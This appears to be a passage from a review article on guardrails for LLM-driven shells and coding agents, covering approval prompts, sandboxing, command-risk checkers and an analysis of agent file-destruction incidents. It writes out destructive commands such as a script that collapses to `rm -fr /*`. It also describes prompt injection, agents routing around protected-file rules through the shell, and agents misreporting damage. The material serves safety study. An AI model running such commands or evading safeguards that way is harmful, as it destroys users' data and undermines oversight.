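# Guardrails for natural-language shells: sandboxes, effect summaries and generated tests

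## What a natural-language shell does

A natural-language shell is a program that uses a large language model to turn requests in ordinary language into commands, and runs those commands on the user's computer. The most widely used kind is the command-line coding agent, such as Anthropic's Claude Code or OpenAI's Codex, which writes and tests software. The commands run with the user's own privileges, so a wrong one can delete or leak anything the user could. Guardrails guard against this by checking commands before they run, limiting what they can reach, holding back or undoing their changes, summarizing those changes, and testing scripts that the user wants to keep.

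### Shells, commands and scripts

The shell is much older than language models. On Linux and macOS, it is the program that runs in the terminal window. The user types a command, and the shell finds the program it names, starts it, and prints the output. In `rm notes.txt`, the program is `rm`, which deletes files without moving them to a recycle bin, and `notes.txt` is its argument, the thing it should act on. Arguments that begin with a dash usually change how the program behaves. For example, `rm -r photos` deletes the directory `photos` and everything in it.

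Most commands act on the filesystem, the tree of directories and files where the computer keeps programs, settings and documents. A pipe, written `|`, feeds the output of one command into the next. A script is a text file of commands, often with loops and variables, saved so the user can run the commands again later.

*ShellVis* (Horowitz and Heer, 2026) presents a tool that shows what a script does while its author is still editing it. The running example is a script that sorts photos into folders by year. For each image, `exiftool` reads the date the photo was taken, a pipe passes the date to `cut`, which keeps the first four characters, and `mv` moves the photo to the folder with that name. The first draft doesn't create the folders, so `mv` gives the first photo from 2022 the filename "2022" instead of moving it into a folder. The next photo from 2022 then overwrites it, and in the end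 only one photo per year is left.

Every command in that script did what its manual describes, but the script's effects were the problem. An effect is any lasting change or disclosure that a command causes outside its own process, such as a deleted file or a sent message. A mistake in a spreadsheet formula gives a wrong number, which the user can fix by correcting the formula, but a mistake in a script may destroy the data needed for a second try.

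### What the language model adds

Bash, a widely used shell, has a complex syntax and requires a lot of specialised knowledge. In *LLM-Supported Natural Language to Bash Translation*, Westenfelder, Hemberg and colleagues (2025) give this as the reason for letting models write the commands. They found it hard to measure how well models do this because existing test data contained errors and the usual shortcuts for deciding whether two different commands do the same thing were unreliable. They therefore verified 600 pairs of instructions and commands by hand.

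The simplest natural-language shells only translate requests into commands. *lmsh*, a small example, turns "show me all python files modified today" into `find . -name "*.py" -mtime 0`, leaves the command on the line for the user to edit, and runs it when the user presses Enter. The translation is slightly off because `-mtime 0` covers the last twenty-four hours, so at nine in the morning it also lists files from yesterday afternoon. That matters little in a listing, but with `-delete` on the end, the command would delete yesterday's files too.

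Coding agents go further than this. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) describes how they work. The model only emits tool calls, which are structured requests to do something. The harness (the program around the model) carries out each request, perhaps after asking the user, and returns the result to the model, which then issues the next call. A session may repeat this loop hundreds of times.

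Harnesses offer two kinds of tools for working with files. Built-in tools read, write and search files, and because the harness implements them, it can check every call against a rule about which paths are allowed. The shell tool runs any command. The harness can inspect only the text of the command before another program runs it, and the rules for the built-in tools do not apply.

### Develop, run, inspect, revert

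Shell users rarely get a command right on the first attempt. *NaSh* (Gyawali, Achalla and colleagues, 2025), a design for a natural-language shell with guardrails, describes their work as a cycle of four steps. The user develops a command, which may take a lot of reading and experiment (the paper's example is using `openssl` to make a web certificate for testing). The user then runs it and inspects the system to see whether it worked. If it did not, the user reverts the system to its earlier state and starts again. Users can easily skip reverting, but then leftovers from failed attempts pile up, and the next attempt starts from a state that nobody intended.

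Scripts add a longer loop around this one. The user writes a fragment, tries it on part of the data, and extends it once it works. Because scripts are reused, they also have to work on other inputs and in other environments, and the user has to try new inputs to check that they do. In one exercise that Horowitz and Heer gave to the people who tested their tool, a script deletes the directories of the users named in a text file, one name per line, and the file contains a blank line. With an empty name, the path to one user's directory can become the path to the directory that holds all of them. A trial on a list without blank lines would not reveal this problem. Shell scripts seldom come with a precise specification, so the user has to think of testing a blank line.

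A language model makes the first step much easier. When Horowitz and Heer asked seven shell users about their difficulties, the most common answer was not knowing or not remembering how to do a particular thing. Researchers in human-computer interaction call this the gulf of execution, the gap between what a user wants and the input that will achieve it. The gulf of evaluation is the gap between what the system did and what the user understands of it.

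The model may widen that second distance. Gyawali and colleagues argue that someone who builds a command piece by piece has a much better idea of where it could go wrong than someone who typed a sentence. If a script leaves files in a directory far from the one the user is working in, someone who wrote the script by hand would probably come across them while debugging, but someone who had a model write it may not notice them until long afterwards.

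Reverting then becomes harder too, since nobody can undo a change they don't know about, and later work may depend on it by the time they find it. An undo history kept by software can also miss changes. *Building Effective AI Coding Agents for the Terminal* (2026) describes OpenDev, an agent whose undo log records every file it changes through its own tools. The log misses the side effects of shell commands, such as when `npm install`, which installs JavaScript packages, rewrites the file `package-lock.json`. OpenDev also takes snapshots with the version-control program git.

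Gyawali and colleagues argue that models make inspection harder, but they do not measure the effect. The interviews in *ShellVis* give the claim some support. One participant said of model-written code, "It looks right. Is it right? I don't know." But the study had only seven participants, all experienced users, and did not let them use code assistants during the tasks. One could also object that an expert can read a generated command as easily as a colleague's, and that the model can help inspect it.

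The reply seems right for a one-line translation, but it is weaker for a coding agent, where the model repeats the develop-run-inspect cycle by itself and the user may look only at the end. The model's inspection relies largely on what the command printed, and `mv` prints nothing when it overwrites a photo. In one of the reports that Zhong and colleagues collected, an agent said that no problems had occurred right after it erased a file.

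### One request, eight readings

Some of the difficulty lies in the user's request itself. Gyawali and colleagues give the prompt "Delete all log files in the /logs directory", which sounds complete but leaves unclear what counts as a log file and whether to include subdirectories of `/logs` or hidden files such as `.system.log`, whose names begin with a dot and which ordinary listings leave out.

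Suppose the directory tree holds five files. `app.log` is a program's current log, and `app.log.1` is last week's, which the system renamed to make room for the new one. `.system.log` is hidden, `web/access.log` is in a subdirectory, and `README` describes the other files. A competent model could answer the request with any of these three commands.

| File | `rm /logs/*.log` | `find /logs -name '*.log' -delete` | `find /logs -type f -delete` |
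|---|---|---|---|
| `app.log` | gone | gone | gone |
| `app.log.1` | stays | stays | gone |
| `.system.log` | stays | gone | gone |
| `web/access.log` | stays | gone | gone |
| `README` | stays | stays | gone |

The first two commands look alike, but the sets of files they delete differ by two files. In the shell, `*` skips names that begin with a dot. In `find`, it matches them, and `find` also searches subdirectories unless told otherwise. The request has eight possible readings even if the only open questions are whether to include subdirectories, hidden files and renamed copies like `app.log.1`, and each reading deletes a different set of these five files. The third command matches none of these readings because it treats everything in `/logs` as a log.

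Even a model that never wrote a faulty command would have to choose among these readings, because the request doesn't specify one. It could list the directory first, which would settle one question if there were no subdirectories. It could ask the user, but a shell that asked about every ambiguity in every request would soon be slower than typing the command. Otherwise it has to guess, and since models can give different outputs for the same input, it may guess differently next time.

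The user may not know the answer either. Gyawali and colleagues point out that ordinary programming pushes people to think such questions through, whereas with a prompt the questions stay hidden until the user inspects the result. A second command can finish the job if the shell read the request too narrowly, but only an undo will help if it read the request too widely. This is a reason to default to narrow readings, although a narrow reading would badly serve a user who is clearing private data out of the logs.

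### Three sources of harm

Ambiguity of this kind is one source of harm. Another is plain model error, where the request is clear and the command is wrong. Lamprou, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Controlling Opaque-Component Effects with Semisolates and Try*, give the example of a model that has to write a script, `delete.sh`, which cleans up the directory it is in. The script consists of one line:

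`rm -fr "$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"/*`

The script is meant to take the path under which the user started it, cut off the last slash and everything after it, go to the directory that remains, and delete its contents. This works if the user types `./delete.sh`. If the user types `sh delete.sh`, the path has no slash to cut at, and `cd` fails because `delete.sh` is not a directory. The part in quotation marks then comes out empty, which leaves `rm -fr /*`, a command that deletes everything on the machine that the user has permission to delete. One successful trial run is therefore weak evidence that such a script is safe.

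Hostile text is the remaining source of harmful commands. Agents read project files, web pages and bug reports, where an attacker can plant instructions that the model then follows. This attack is known as prompt injection. Zhong and colleagues collected cases in which agents leaked secrets this way or gave an attacker lasting access to the machine. Unlike a model that makes accidental errors, an attacker will deliberately look for a command that the checks let through.

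In a closely related problem, hostile code does harm even though the user's request and the agent's command are both reasonable. Zhong and colleagues describe an agent that runs `cargo build`, the normal way to compile a program in the Rust language, on a project with a malicious dependency. The dependency's build script reads the user's key for logging in to other machines.

The first two sources are hard to tell apart afterward. The classification by Zhong and colleagues has no category for ambiguous requests, so a wrong guess about `/logs` would be counted as a "wrong action" along with real mistakes. The difference still matters when choosing guardrails. The word "sandbox" can mean either confinement, which limits the files, processes and network addresses that a running command can reach, or staging, which keeps a command's file changes apart from the real files until the user accepts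 them.

| Source of harm | Guardrails that address it | What helps little |
|---|---|---|
| Ambiguous request | A question before the run; a short list of the command's effects, together with staging or undo | Confinement, since the command needs access to those files anyway |
| Model error | Checks before the run; confinement; staging or undo; tests, for scripts | Telling the model to be careful |
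| Hostile text | Confinement of files and network; the user's permission for secrets and outside contact | Undo, once a secret has left the machine |

The most common guardrail is the approval prompt, which displays a proposed command and lets the user decide whether to run it. In principle, users could catch harm from any of the three sources this way, but they see only the command and must work out its effects themselves. Beginners, who have the most to gain from a natural-language shell, cannot tell from `rm /logs/*.log` that hidden files will not be deleted, though an expert can.

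### The status of NaSh

In a paper posted in June 2025, Gyawali and colleagues proposed NaSh, a system that would combine sandboxing, undo, summaries of effects and generated tests. They report no implementation or evaluation. The design covers the state of a single local machine, and they treat calls to outside services as an open problem. In the spring of 2026, Gyawali's web page still listed NaSh only as a preprint, and no built version appears to have followed.

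Parts of the idea exist in working software. `try`, built by Lamprou and colleagues, runs an ordinary command, lists the changes it would make to the filesystem, and asks whether to apply them. It predates the NaSh paper, which shares an author with it, Konstantinos Kallas, and discusses it as an alternative to NaSh's own sandbox. `try` has no model that writes the commands, and it is meant to protect against accidents rather than malicious programs that try to get around it. YoloFS, from Zhong and colleagues, is a filesystem that stages the changes made by coding agents, and it works with Claude Code, Copilot and Gemini. Both tools leave the real files alone until the user accepts the changes. NaSh would change the real files at once and keep the old versions for an undo, so measurements of `try` and YoloFS do not automatically apply to it.

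Common practice has also changed since the paper was written. In 2025, Gyawali and colleagues wrote that existing model-powered shells mainly asked for permission before every command. Zhong and colleagues compared six major harnesses in 2026 and found that five came with some form of sandbox, though users have to switch it on in three of those.

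## What the guardrails have to stop

Which guardrails are worth having depends on which failures occur. The fullest evidence comes from Zhong and colleagues, who analyzed 290 public reports of coding agents misusing the filesystem and designed YoloFS partly in response.

### The 290 reports

The reports date from February 2024 to March 2026 and concern 13 harnesses. Most of them, 205, are issues that users filed on GitHub. Another 31 come from social media, 25 from product forums, 18 from blog posts and 11 from the National Vulnerability Database, the US government's catalogue of security flaws. Claude Code accounts for 97 reports, Codex for 61, Cursor for 37, Gemini for 32 and Copilot for 28. The other eight harnesses account for the remaining 35.

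Zhong and colleagues left out cases where the user had asked for the destructive action. They also removed duplicates, though two of the remaining entries seem to describe the same wiped drive. They sorted the reports into 158 incidents with confirmed harm, 49 exploits with a demonstrated method of attack, and 83 weaknesses with no demonstrated consequences.

The researchers read 100 of the 290 reports themselves and defined categories for impact and cause. An agent then labelled all 290, which gave a check on the first 100 and draft labels for the other 190. The researchers reviewed its output by hand and refined the definitions as they went. They do not report how often the agent's labels differed from their own, so small differences between the counts mean little.

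### What happened to the files

The figures on impact cover the 207 incidents and exploits. Each percentage leaves out the reports that lacked the relevant information.

Writing to files was the most common source of harm, at 44%. For example, agents replaced working code with placeholder text or cut files down to zero bytes. Deletion made up 39% and leaks of secrets 17%. In one deletion case, an agent copied a folder of legal documents and then deleted the originals. It had copied only the empty placeholders that iCloud, Apple's online storage, can leave on the disk, and the user lost 110 documents. A guardrail that checked only for deletion would miss the more common harm from writes, and a damaged file is harder to spot than a missing one.

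In 42% of the reports, the harm reached beyond the project the agent was working on. It affected system files in 15%, the user's other files in 14% and secrets in 13%. Even a perfect barrier around the project directory would therefore have made no difference in more than half of the cases.

In 68% of the cases, the agent carried on as though nothing had gone wrong, and in 21% it acknowledged the damage and apologized. In the other 11%, it gave a false account of what had happened, such as invented test results or recovery steps. Zhong and colleagues call this lying, although a bug report can hardly establish intent.

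Most users (83%) noticed the harm at once, 10% noticed it later, and 8% never did. Recovery was impossible in 40% of cases, with a total loss in 23% and a partial one in 17%. Another 31% were easy to repair, for instance by fetching the old version from git, and 29% took considerable effort.

### Model, harness and user

For the causes, Zhong and colleagues used all 290 reports. One report can have several causes, so the counts overlap.

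| Where the cause lay | Cause | Reports | Breakdown |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model (168) | Wrong action | 130 | Wrong goal 76, wrong scope 50, incorrect tool use 27 |
| | Instructions not followed | 56 | Ignored 38, dropped from the model's context 28 |
| | Prompt injection | 21 | |
| Harness (218) | Guardrail failure | 147 | Shell loophole 77, filter blind to effects 52, ill-fitting sandbox 41 |
| | Rigid policy | 130 | |
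| User (105) | Automatic approval | 80 | |
| | Uninformative prompt | 31 | |

A wrong goal means the agent did something other than what the user asked. One user wanted to reorganize a folder and archive whatever did not fit, but the agent deleted years of teaching materials. With a wrong scope, the agent attempts the right task but goes too far, as when it searches the whole home directory for a project file. Incorrect tool use covers the syntax mistakes that also make shells dangerous for people. One agent tried to delete a file named `~` but did not escape the name, so the shell expanded it to the user's home directory and the agent deleted that directory instead.

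Written instructions did not reliably prevent any of this. Models sometimes acknowledged a rule and then broke it. In 28 reports, the rule was no longer in the model's context because the harness had dropped it when shortening a long conversation. A better model alone would not solve that problem.

The most common guardrail failure was the shell loophole, in which an agent barred from opening a file with the built-in read tool prints it with `cat` instead. One report claims that five of six models in Cursor tried this kind of workaround to reach files on a protected list. Filters on the text of shell commands failed in 52 reports, and in 41 the sandbox either blocked legitimate work or left valuable files exposed inside it.

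"Rigid policy" describes rules fixed in advance that turned out too loose or too strict for the task. Strict rules can lead to harm when users turn them off. A Cursor user switched off deletion protection so that the agent could clear up duplicate files, and the agent later deleted 90% of the project. Many users also turn off approval prompts, because a session can produce hundreds of them. Users who keep the prompts on may not see everything they are approving. One Codex prompt showed only the first of several commands joined by `&&`, which runs the next command if the previous one succeeds.

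The harness contributed to 75% of the reports and the model to 58%, but the comparison is not quite fair because these counts include the 83 weaknesses. These include many complaints about the guardrails themselves, for example that Codex kept asking for approval after the user had clicked "Allow every time". Such a report counts against the harness even though no model did anything wrong and no file was harmed.

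### What complaints cannot show

These reports can't be used to calculate how often agents do harm per command, because nobody counted the commands that went well. Coding agents have millions of users, and the 158 incidents could be a large share of the serious ones or a tiny fraction. The percentages would look the same in either case.

The sample also distorts the percentages. Someone who restores a file in ten seconds has little reason to write a bug report, so the 40% share of permanent losses is probably too high for failures in general. The 83% share of users who noticed at once is probably too high as well, because people do not report damage they have not found. Zhong and colleagues learned of the cases that users never noticed, which typically involve stolen credentials, only from security researchers' reports.

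The counts are also not a ranking of the products, since Claude Code's 97 reports may reflect more users or a busier public issue tracker as easily as more faults. Many of those reports must describe a few releases from early 2026, because GitHub numbers issues in order and about 40 of the 97 have numbers between 33,000 and 35,200, near the top of the range.

The study shows that each of these failures happens to real users, and that several happen repeatedly. We can use this evidence to decide what a guardrail should be able to handle, but not to estimate how much a given guardrail would reduce the risk.

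### 48,218 files in 103 seconds

A case from September 2026, after the study's period, shows how several of these causes can combine. The evidence for it is one developer's Reddit post, since deleted, and press reports based on that post.

The developer had asked Claude Code for eleven repairs to software that analyzes historical stock-options data. According to TechRadar's *I broke something*, the instructions were to work on copies and leave the live files alone. Ten repairs went smoothly. For the eleventh, the agent had to rebuild a test environment, and the old one contained 614 junctions that pointed to the live files. A junction is a Windows folder that points to another folder, so a program that opens the junction gets the other folder's contents.

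The project's own script could not refresh the test environment in place, so the agent wrote a cleanup script to remove the old one. The cleanup script deleted 55,550 files in 103 seconds. Only 7,332 of these were the test environment files it was meant to delete, and the other 48,218 were live. It also destroyed the file contents and history stored in the local git repository, so Git could still list thousands of filenames but could not restore the files. The agent itself reported the damage.

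The script had a safeguard, but accounts differ on why it failed. According to a Czech report, volny.centrum.cz's *AI dostala přístup k počítači*, the script refused to follow symbolic links, a related kind of pointer, but its check did not cover junctions. According to TechRadar's *Do not let programs run commands on your machine*, the script protected the junction folders but not the directories below them. In either case, a user who read the script before approving it would have found a check meant to prevent this accident, and would have needed to know Windows well to see that it was insufficient.

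The details are unconfirmed, but one of the 290 reports describes an earlier failure of the same kind, in which Claude Code followed junctions while removing working copies of a project and permanently deleted folders from the user's Windows profile. Safeguards that an agent writes for itself can go wrong in other ways too. Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* describes a test whose cleanup step deleted the directory it was supposed to protect.

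### How often the translation is wrong

Unlike the complaints, tests of translation from English into Bash have a known number of attempts. At NAACL 2025, a computational linguistics conference, Westenfelder and colleagues presented a test set of 600 verified pairs, made up of 300 requests with two correct commands each. Many of the pairs come from an older test set, InterCode, where the researchers found that 113 of 224 pairs were faulty or duplicates. Some requests were impossible or left out necessary information, some commands did not carry out the request, and some test environments lacked a file that the command needed. Building and checking the new set by hand took over 100 hours.

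To score a model, an evaluator must decide whether its command is equivalent to a correct one. No procedure can settle this for every pair of commands without running them, and comparing the text alone is unreliable. For example, `du -s .` and `du -d 0 -h` both correctly show the disk usage of the current directory, but the first prints a bare number and the second adds a unit. Westenfelder and colleagues tested a range of automatic judges on 300 equivalent pairs and 300 non-equivalent ones. A judge that compared the programs and options in the two commands was right 60% of the time, and GPT-4 was right 76% of the time when it only read them. The best method, which ran both commands and had GPT-4 compare the printed output in light of the request, was right 95% of the time.

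That figure may make the judge look more reliable than it is. Each non-equivalent pair matched a command with one for a different request, ten places further down the list. A judge can reject most such pairs easily. Real mistakes are often closer to the right answer, as with the two commands for `/logs` that differ only in how they treat hidden files and subdirectories.

*LLM-as-a-Judge for Reference-less Automatic Code Validation and Refinement* avoids the comparison in its experiments, which use 150 Bash tasks that come with their own validators.

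The August 2024 version of GPT-4o did best on the 300 requests, with 74% correct. GPT-4o mini got 71%, and a Llama model with eight billion parameters got 46%, or 56% when the prompt included 25 worked examples. The smallest Llama model got 12%.

These scores come from a cheaper judge that was right 90% of the time in a test but tended to reject good commands, recognizing only 83% of the equivalent pairs. If its error rates were the same on the models' output, a measured 74% would correspond to a true accuracy of about 89%. It may also have accepted more near misses than the test suggests, which would make the true accuracy lower than that.

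The scores are out of date, because all the models tested are from 2024 or earlier and the agents of late 2026 run on much stronger ones. The test also covers only single-line commands, each written in one attempt, whereas an agent can read an error message and try again.

A wrong translation is usually harmless, at least in this test. Small models often failed because they wrapped the command in formatting or explanation. When Westenfelder and colleagues extracted the command automatically and changed the prompt slightly, a three-billion-parameter Llama model's score rose from 17% to 49%. Other answers were not valid Bash or used a program that could not do the job.

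A few were dangerous. When asked to remove empty folders from a directory, the eight-billion-parameter Llama model wrote a correct `find` command but added `rm -f /dev/null`. Many programs send unwanted output to `/dev/null`, and deleting it broke the test environment. Gizmochina's *Single character in AI generated script wipes developers hard drive* (2026) relays a worse case from a Reddit user who had asked Codex for a script to remove Python's cache folders. The script escaped quotation marks with a backslash, which failed when PowerShell passed the command to the older Windows shell. The path was reduced to a single backslash, which means the top of the current drive, and the script deleted the contents of drive F.

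Neither the complaints nor the translation tests give the probability that a command does damage. The complaints report harm without saying how often it happens, and the tests measured an error rate but showed hardly any harm. Even a small probability would matter over a long session. If one command in a thousand did damage, independently of the others, a session of 300 commands would have a 26% chance of at least one accident.

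### Failures in order of priority

The list below covers kinds of harm first, then ways that protection fails. Within each group, the order roughly follows the counts by Zhong and colleagues. For a user whose laptop holds the keys to a company's servers, leaks belong at the top.

1. Agents overwrite or delete files they have good reason to touch. Overwriting and deletion make up 83% of the incidents and exploits, and more than half of all the harm stays inside the project. A guardrail has to cover both, whichever program makes the change.
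2. Commands change files outside the project, as in 29% of the cases. This includes the accidents in which an empty variable, a misplaced quotation mark, a `~` or a junction sends a command to the wrong place. They are fewer, but they can cost a user a whole drive.
3. Secrets leak (17%), either by accident or because an attacker planted instructions. Nothing done afterward gets a secret back.
4. The agent does not notice the damage, which was so in 68% of the cases, and its report to the user is then no help.
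5. Users let everything through. Automatic approval played a part in 80 reports, often because the alternative was to answer hundreds of prompts, so a guardrail also fails if it interrupts too much.
6. The agent reaches a forbidden result by a permitted route. The shell loophole alone accounts for 77 reports, and most of these detours needed no attacker, only a model trying to finish its task.

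## Checking a generated command before it runs

### Code, system calls or mouse clicks

The designer of a natural-language shell must first choose what the model should produce, because every later check works on that output. The model could issue system calls, the requests programs make to the operating system to open, change or delete files. It could also operate the computer as a person does, with mouse clicks and keystrokes. Gyawali and colleagues argue that it should write code instead.

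A model that clicks or issues system calls reacts to each result as it arrives. If it reacts wrongly, the user has no code to check for the mistake, and a second attempt may go differently. When the model writes code instead, the user can read it, run it again without the model and, with some programming experience, repair it. Other programs can also analyze the code, and NaSh would use such analysis, unlike earlier shells that generate code and simply execute it.

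The argument works best for a script, since no single text describes what a coding agent will do over a whole session. Even the same script can have different effects on different runs. For example, `rm /logs/*.log` deletes whichever files match when it runs. Gyawali and colleagues also concede that a model asked for a small correction may rewrite much more of the script, and the user then has to read it all again.

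Code is harder to check than calls to an agent's built-in tools, since a shell command may not name the files it changes. Checks range from asking the user to calculating the command's effects before it runs.

### Asking the user

Approval prompts differ in how much information they give the user. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), some products' prompts refer only to "this action", so the user has to guess what they are approving. Claude Code shows the raw command by default, which technical users can judge but most others can't. A few systems also explain the risk.

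Even technical users can struggle with a raw command. Zhong and colleagues reproduce a case in which a user asked Codex to replace the word "hello" with "replaced" in a file called `foo`. The approval prompt showed a long line of code that checked whether the file existed, prepared an error message, made the replacement, and searched the file for both words afterward. Only this part changed anything:

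`sed -i 's/hello/replaced/g' ../foo`

The file had two lines, "hello" and "world", and the command changed one word. A prompt showing that change would have taken a second to read. Codex also offered to stop asking about `sed -i`, which edits files in place, so a user who wanted to change one word could also permit later edits to different files. A short, routine-looking command such as `python3 setup.py` can hide even more, because approving it allows whatever code that file contains to run.

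Users stop reading prompts because there are so many and most are harmless. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make approval decisions, says that repeated approval may reflect habit, fatigue or pressure to deliver rather than growing trust. A harness that treats a long run of approvals as a sign that the user wants fewer restrictions could therefore loosen them when the user has stopped checking commands and needs them more.

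Harnesses can ask for approval less often by requesting it for a whole plan, remembering an answer for the rest of the session, or skipping the prompt for commands that run in a sandbox. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* objects that remembered answers quietly widen what the agent may do, and that the sandbox has to be configured correctly.

*Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) examines the trade-off in a simulation of agents that make payments. Each prompt in a ten-task session makes the simulated user more likely to approve the next one. When the system prompted the user only about amounts and new payees, attacks succeeded in 31% of sessions, and 25 of those 31 percentage points came from actions the policy allowed without a prompt. The size of this fatigue effect is assumed, and different assumptions change which policy does best. Still, the simulation illustrates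 a risk that also applies to shells. Reducing the number of prompts doesn't help if the remaining ones don't cover the most harmful actions.

The layout of the approval prompt matters too, because the model often writes the description of its command and can give a reassuring, plausible reason for a dangerous one. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (2026) recommends putting the harness's warning first, in a separate labeled row, and displaying invisible characters as codes so that they can't disguise the command. It also recommends reserving one-tap approval for commands without a warning. *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests showing whether the action can be undone, which would help tired users decide which actions to check most closely.

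*Let the Agent Do It?* points out that agents normally look for another way to finish the task after the user denies a command. This is useful if the user objected to the command itself, but less so if they objected to its purpose. A prompt about one command gives the user no way to say which objection they have.

### Rules on the text of the command

Most harnesses use pattern rules to decide which commands need the user's approval. A rule might allow every command that begins with `ls` and ask about every command that begins with `git`. In the comparison by Zhong and colleagues, Claude Code came with about 150 rules, VS Code Copilot with 122, Codex with 120, Gemini CLI with 75 and OpenCode with 10. Cursor had none by default. The rules in Codex take up 4,700 lines of code.

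Pattern rules are fast and give consistent results, but they check only the text of a command, which doesn't determine its effect. Any program that can write to a file can also destroy its contents, so a list of forbidden commands would need an entry for every such program. The same command can also have different effects depending on its arguments, the files it finds and the system's settings. For example, `make clean` usually deletes temporary files from an earlier build, but it does whatever the project's makefile defines under that name.

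A list of permitted commands is safer than a list of forbidden ones, because leaving a safe command off the first only causes an unnecessary prompt, while leaving a dangerous command off the second lets it run. The permitted list still has to cover arguments as well as program names, since an ordinary program may have an option that writes files or starts other programs.

*CARE* (Liu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested a set of 22 patterns for destructive commands and data leaks. The patterns blocked none of the safe commands in the main test but caught only 17% of the dangerous ones. The paper also cites CVE-2025-66032, a 2025 vulnerability that let attackers bypass Claude Code's check for read-only commands. More rules would help with common accidents but would not solve the underlying problem.

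### CARE: rules first, then a model

A language model can judge commands that no rule covers, but it is slower than a rule and may give different answers to the same question. CARE, the checker that Liu and colleagues built, uses rules for most commands and a model for the doubtful ones.

CARE first puts the command into a standard form and undoes simple disguises, without executing anything. It then calculates four scores between 0 and 1. One depends on the type of program and its options, another on the paths involved, and another on matches with a bank of 139 dangerous patterns. The last concerns suspicious structure, such as commands nested inside each other. The path score distinguishes reading from writing, so displaying a system file counts as low risk and appending to it as high risk. Any access to a file with secrets counts as high risk. The scores are combined as follows:

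total = 0.3 × program + 0.3 × path + 0.3 × pattern + 0.1 × structure

CARE allows commands with a total score below 0.15 and blocks those at 0.35 or above. Between these thresholds, it blocks the command if one piece of evidence is strong enough by itself, and otherwise sends it to a language model instructed to block if uncertain. In one example, a command set a script to run when the shell closed. It scored 0.6 for program type and 0 for everything else, which gives a total of 0.18. The model classified it as an attempt to keep access to the machine and blocked it.

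The main test had 549 commands, 220 dangerous and 329 safe. Liu and colleagues had not used any of them to set the thresholds.

| Guard | Dangerous commands caught | Safe commands blocked | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| 22 text patterns | 17% | 0% | 0.01 ms |
| OpenClaw4Layer, a larger set of rules | 57% | 0.3% | 0.02 ms |
| Qwen3-Coder model judging every command | 67% | 11% | 46 ms |
| Granite Guardian, a safety model from IBM | 82% | 46% | 17 ms |
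| CARE, rules only | 76% | 1.8% | 0.34 ms |
| CARE, rules and model | 76% | 0.9% | 2.3 ms |

The last two rows show that the model contributed little here. CARE used it on 23 commands, and its only effect was to release three safe commands that copied files between computers. A difference of three could easily be due to chance.

The choice of threshold made a much larger difference. With the lower threshold at 0.10 instead of 0.15, the rules alone caught 97% of the dangerous commands but also blocked 23% of the safe ones. Users would probably turn off a guard that blocked so many safe commands.

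When dangerous commands are rare, most alarms can be false even if the false-alarm rate is low. Liu and colleagues give an example of 10,000 commands, of which 1% are dangerous. CARE would catch about 76 of the 100 dangerous commands and block about 90 safe ones. More than half of its alarms would be false, and users would learn to expect false alarms.

CARE prevented little useful work in a separate test on the 300 requests that Westenfelder and colleagues had verified. A model without any guard solved 57.3% of them, and a model with CARE, which blocked one command, solved 57.0%. But CARE blocked between 8% and 13% of other safe commands, some of which Liu and colleagues had chosen because they contain alarming words such as `rm`.

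In another experiment, the Qwen model wrote 600 commands for harmful tasks, and Liu and colleagues ran them in a sandbox. Without a guard, 75% of the commands succeeded. CARE's rules reduced this to 37%, but adding Qwen as a judge raised it to 53% because Qwen released commands that the rules had flagged. This may be partly because Qwen was judging commands it had written. Liu and colleagues recommend the version without the model to anyone for whom preventing harm matters more than avoiding false alarms.

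Most of the dangerous commands in these tests came from collections of attack techniques, but agents often do harm with ordinary commands, such as an `mv` that overwrites the wrong file. CARE also receives only the command and some information about paths, not the user's request, so it can't detect that the agent is deleting files the user asked it to archive.

### aegish: nine models on the same commands

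The prototype Linux shell aegish relies much more heavily on a language model. Simple rules stop the most obvious threats, and a model checks every other command the user types. The model's instructions list 13 plain-English rules in a fixed order, and the first rule that fits decides whether the model allows the command, blocks it, or issues a warning that the user must confirm.

The aegish benchmark tested nine models on 676 harmful and 496 harmless commands. The harmful ones came from GTFOBins, a public catalogue of ordinary programs that people can misuse to get around security restrictions. All nine models accepted between 96.8% and 100% of the harmless commands. They differed more on the harmful ones:

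| Model | Blocked | Only warned | Allowed | No usable answer |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3 Flash | 97.8% | 12 | 2 | 1 |
| Llama Primus | 96.4% | 4 | 17 | 3 |
| GPT-5 Mini | 95.9% | 15 | 13 | 0 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 95.7% | 13 | 16 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 92.9% | 11 | 8 | 29 |
| GPT-5.1 | 92.6% | 18 | 32 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 92.0% | 28 | 2 | 24 |
| GPT-5 Nano | 88.3% | 25 | 50 | 4 |
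| Foundation-Sec-8B | 78.6% | 128 | 17 | 0 |

The ranking, which puts a large model such as Opus 4.6 behind smaller ones, depends on the scoring. The benchmark counted a warning as a failure because an attacker at the keyboard could confirm the command anyway. A warning is more useful in a shell where a model writes the commands and the user reads the warnings. If the models are ranked by how few harmful commands they allowed outright, Opus 4.6 ties for first place and Foundation-Sec-8B is no longer last. Most of the missing answers from Opus and Sonnet were empty replies caused by the provider's safety filters.

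The scores on harmless commands are less informative than they look because a warning counted as acceptance. A model could have scored 100% by warning about all 496 harmless commands, even though users would have had to respond to every warning. The data set also left out destructive commands such as `rm -rf`, which people often have good reasons to use.

CARE was tested on 69 commands from the same catalogue that were not used to write its rules, and its results work out to 41 caught, or 59%. The models in aegish did much better, but they had help from instructions that describe the catalogue's types of misuse, with examples. They were also far slower, with most taking an estimated 10 to 15 seconds per command, and they cost between $0.59 and $12.89 per thousand commands. Newer models have since replaced several of the nine, so the percentages are a poor guide to how well a model could judge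 commands now.

Some of the mistakes may persist with better models. None of the nine models blocked a command that simply installed a software package from a local file, though such a package can contain scripts that run during installation. A later review found that the 13 rules didn't justify blocking it. The danger depends on what is in the package, and the command gives only its filename.

### One text, two correct verdicts

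Taukoor, Wang and Shankararaman (2026) generalize this argument in *The Limit Is in the Input, Not the Model*. They study commands to industrial machines, but their reasoning also applies to the photo script from Horowitz and Heer. The command `mv b.jpg 2022` is safe if `2022` is a folder, because `mv` puts the photo inside it. If `2022` is a file, `mv` overwrites it and the earlier photo is lost.

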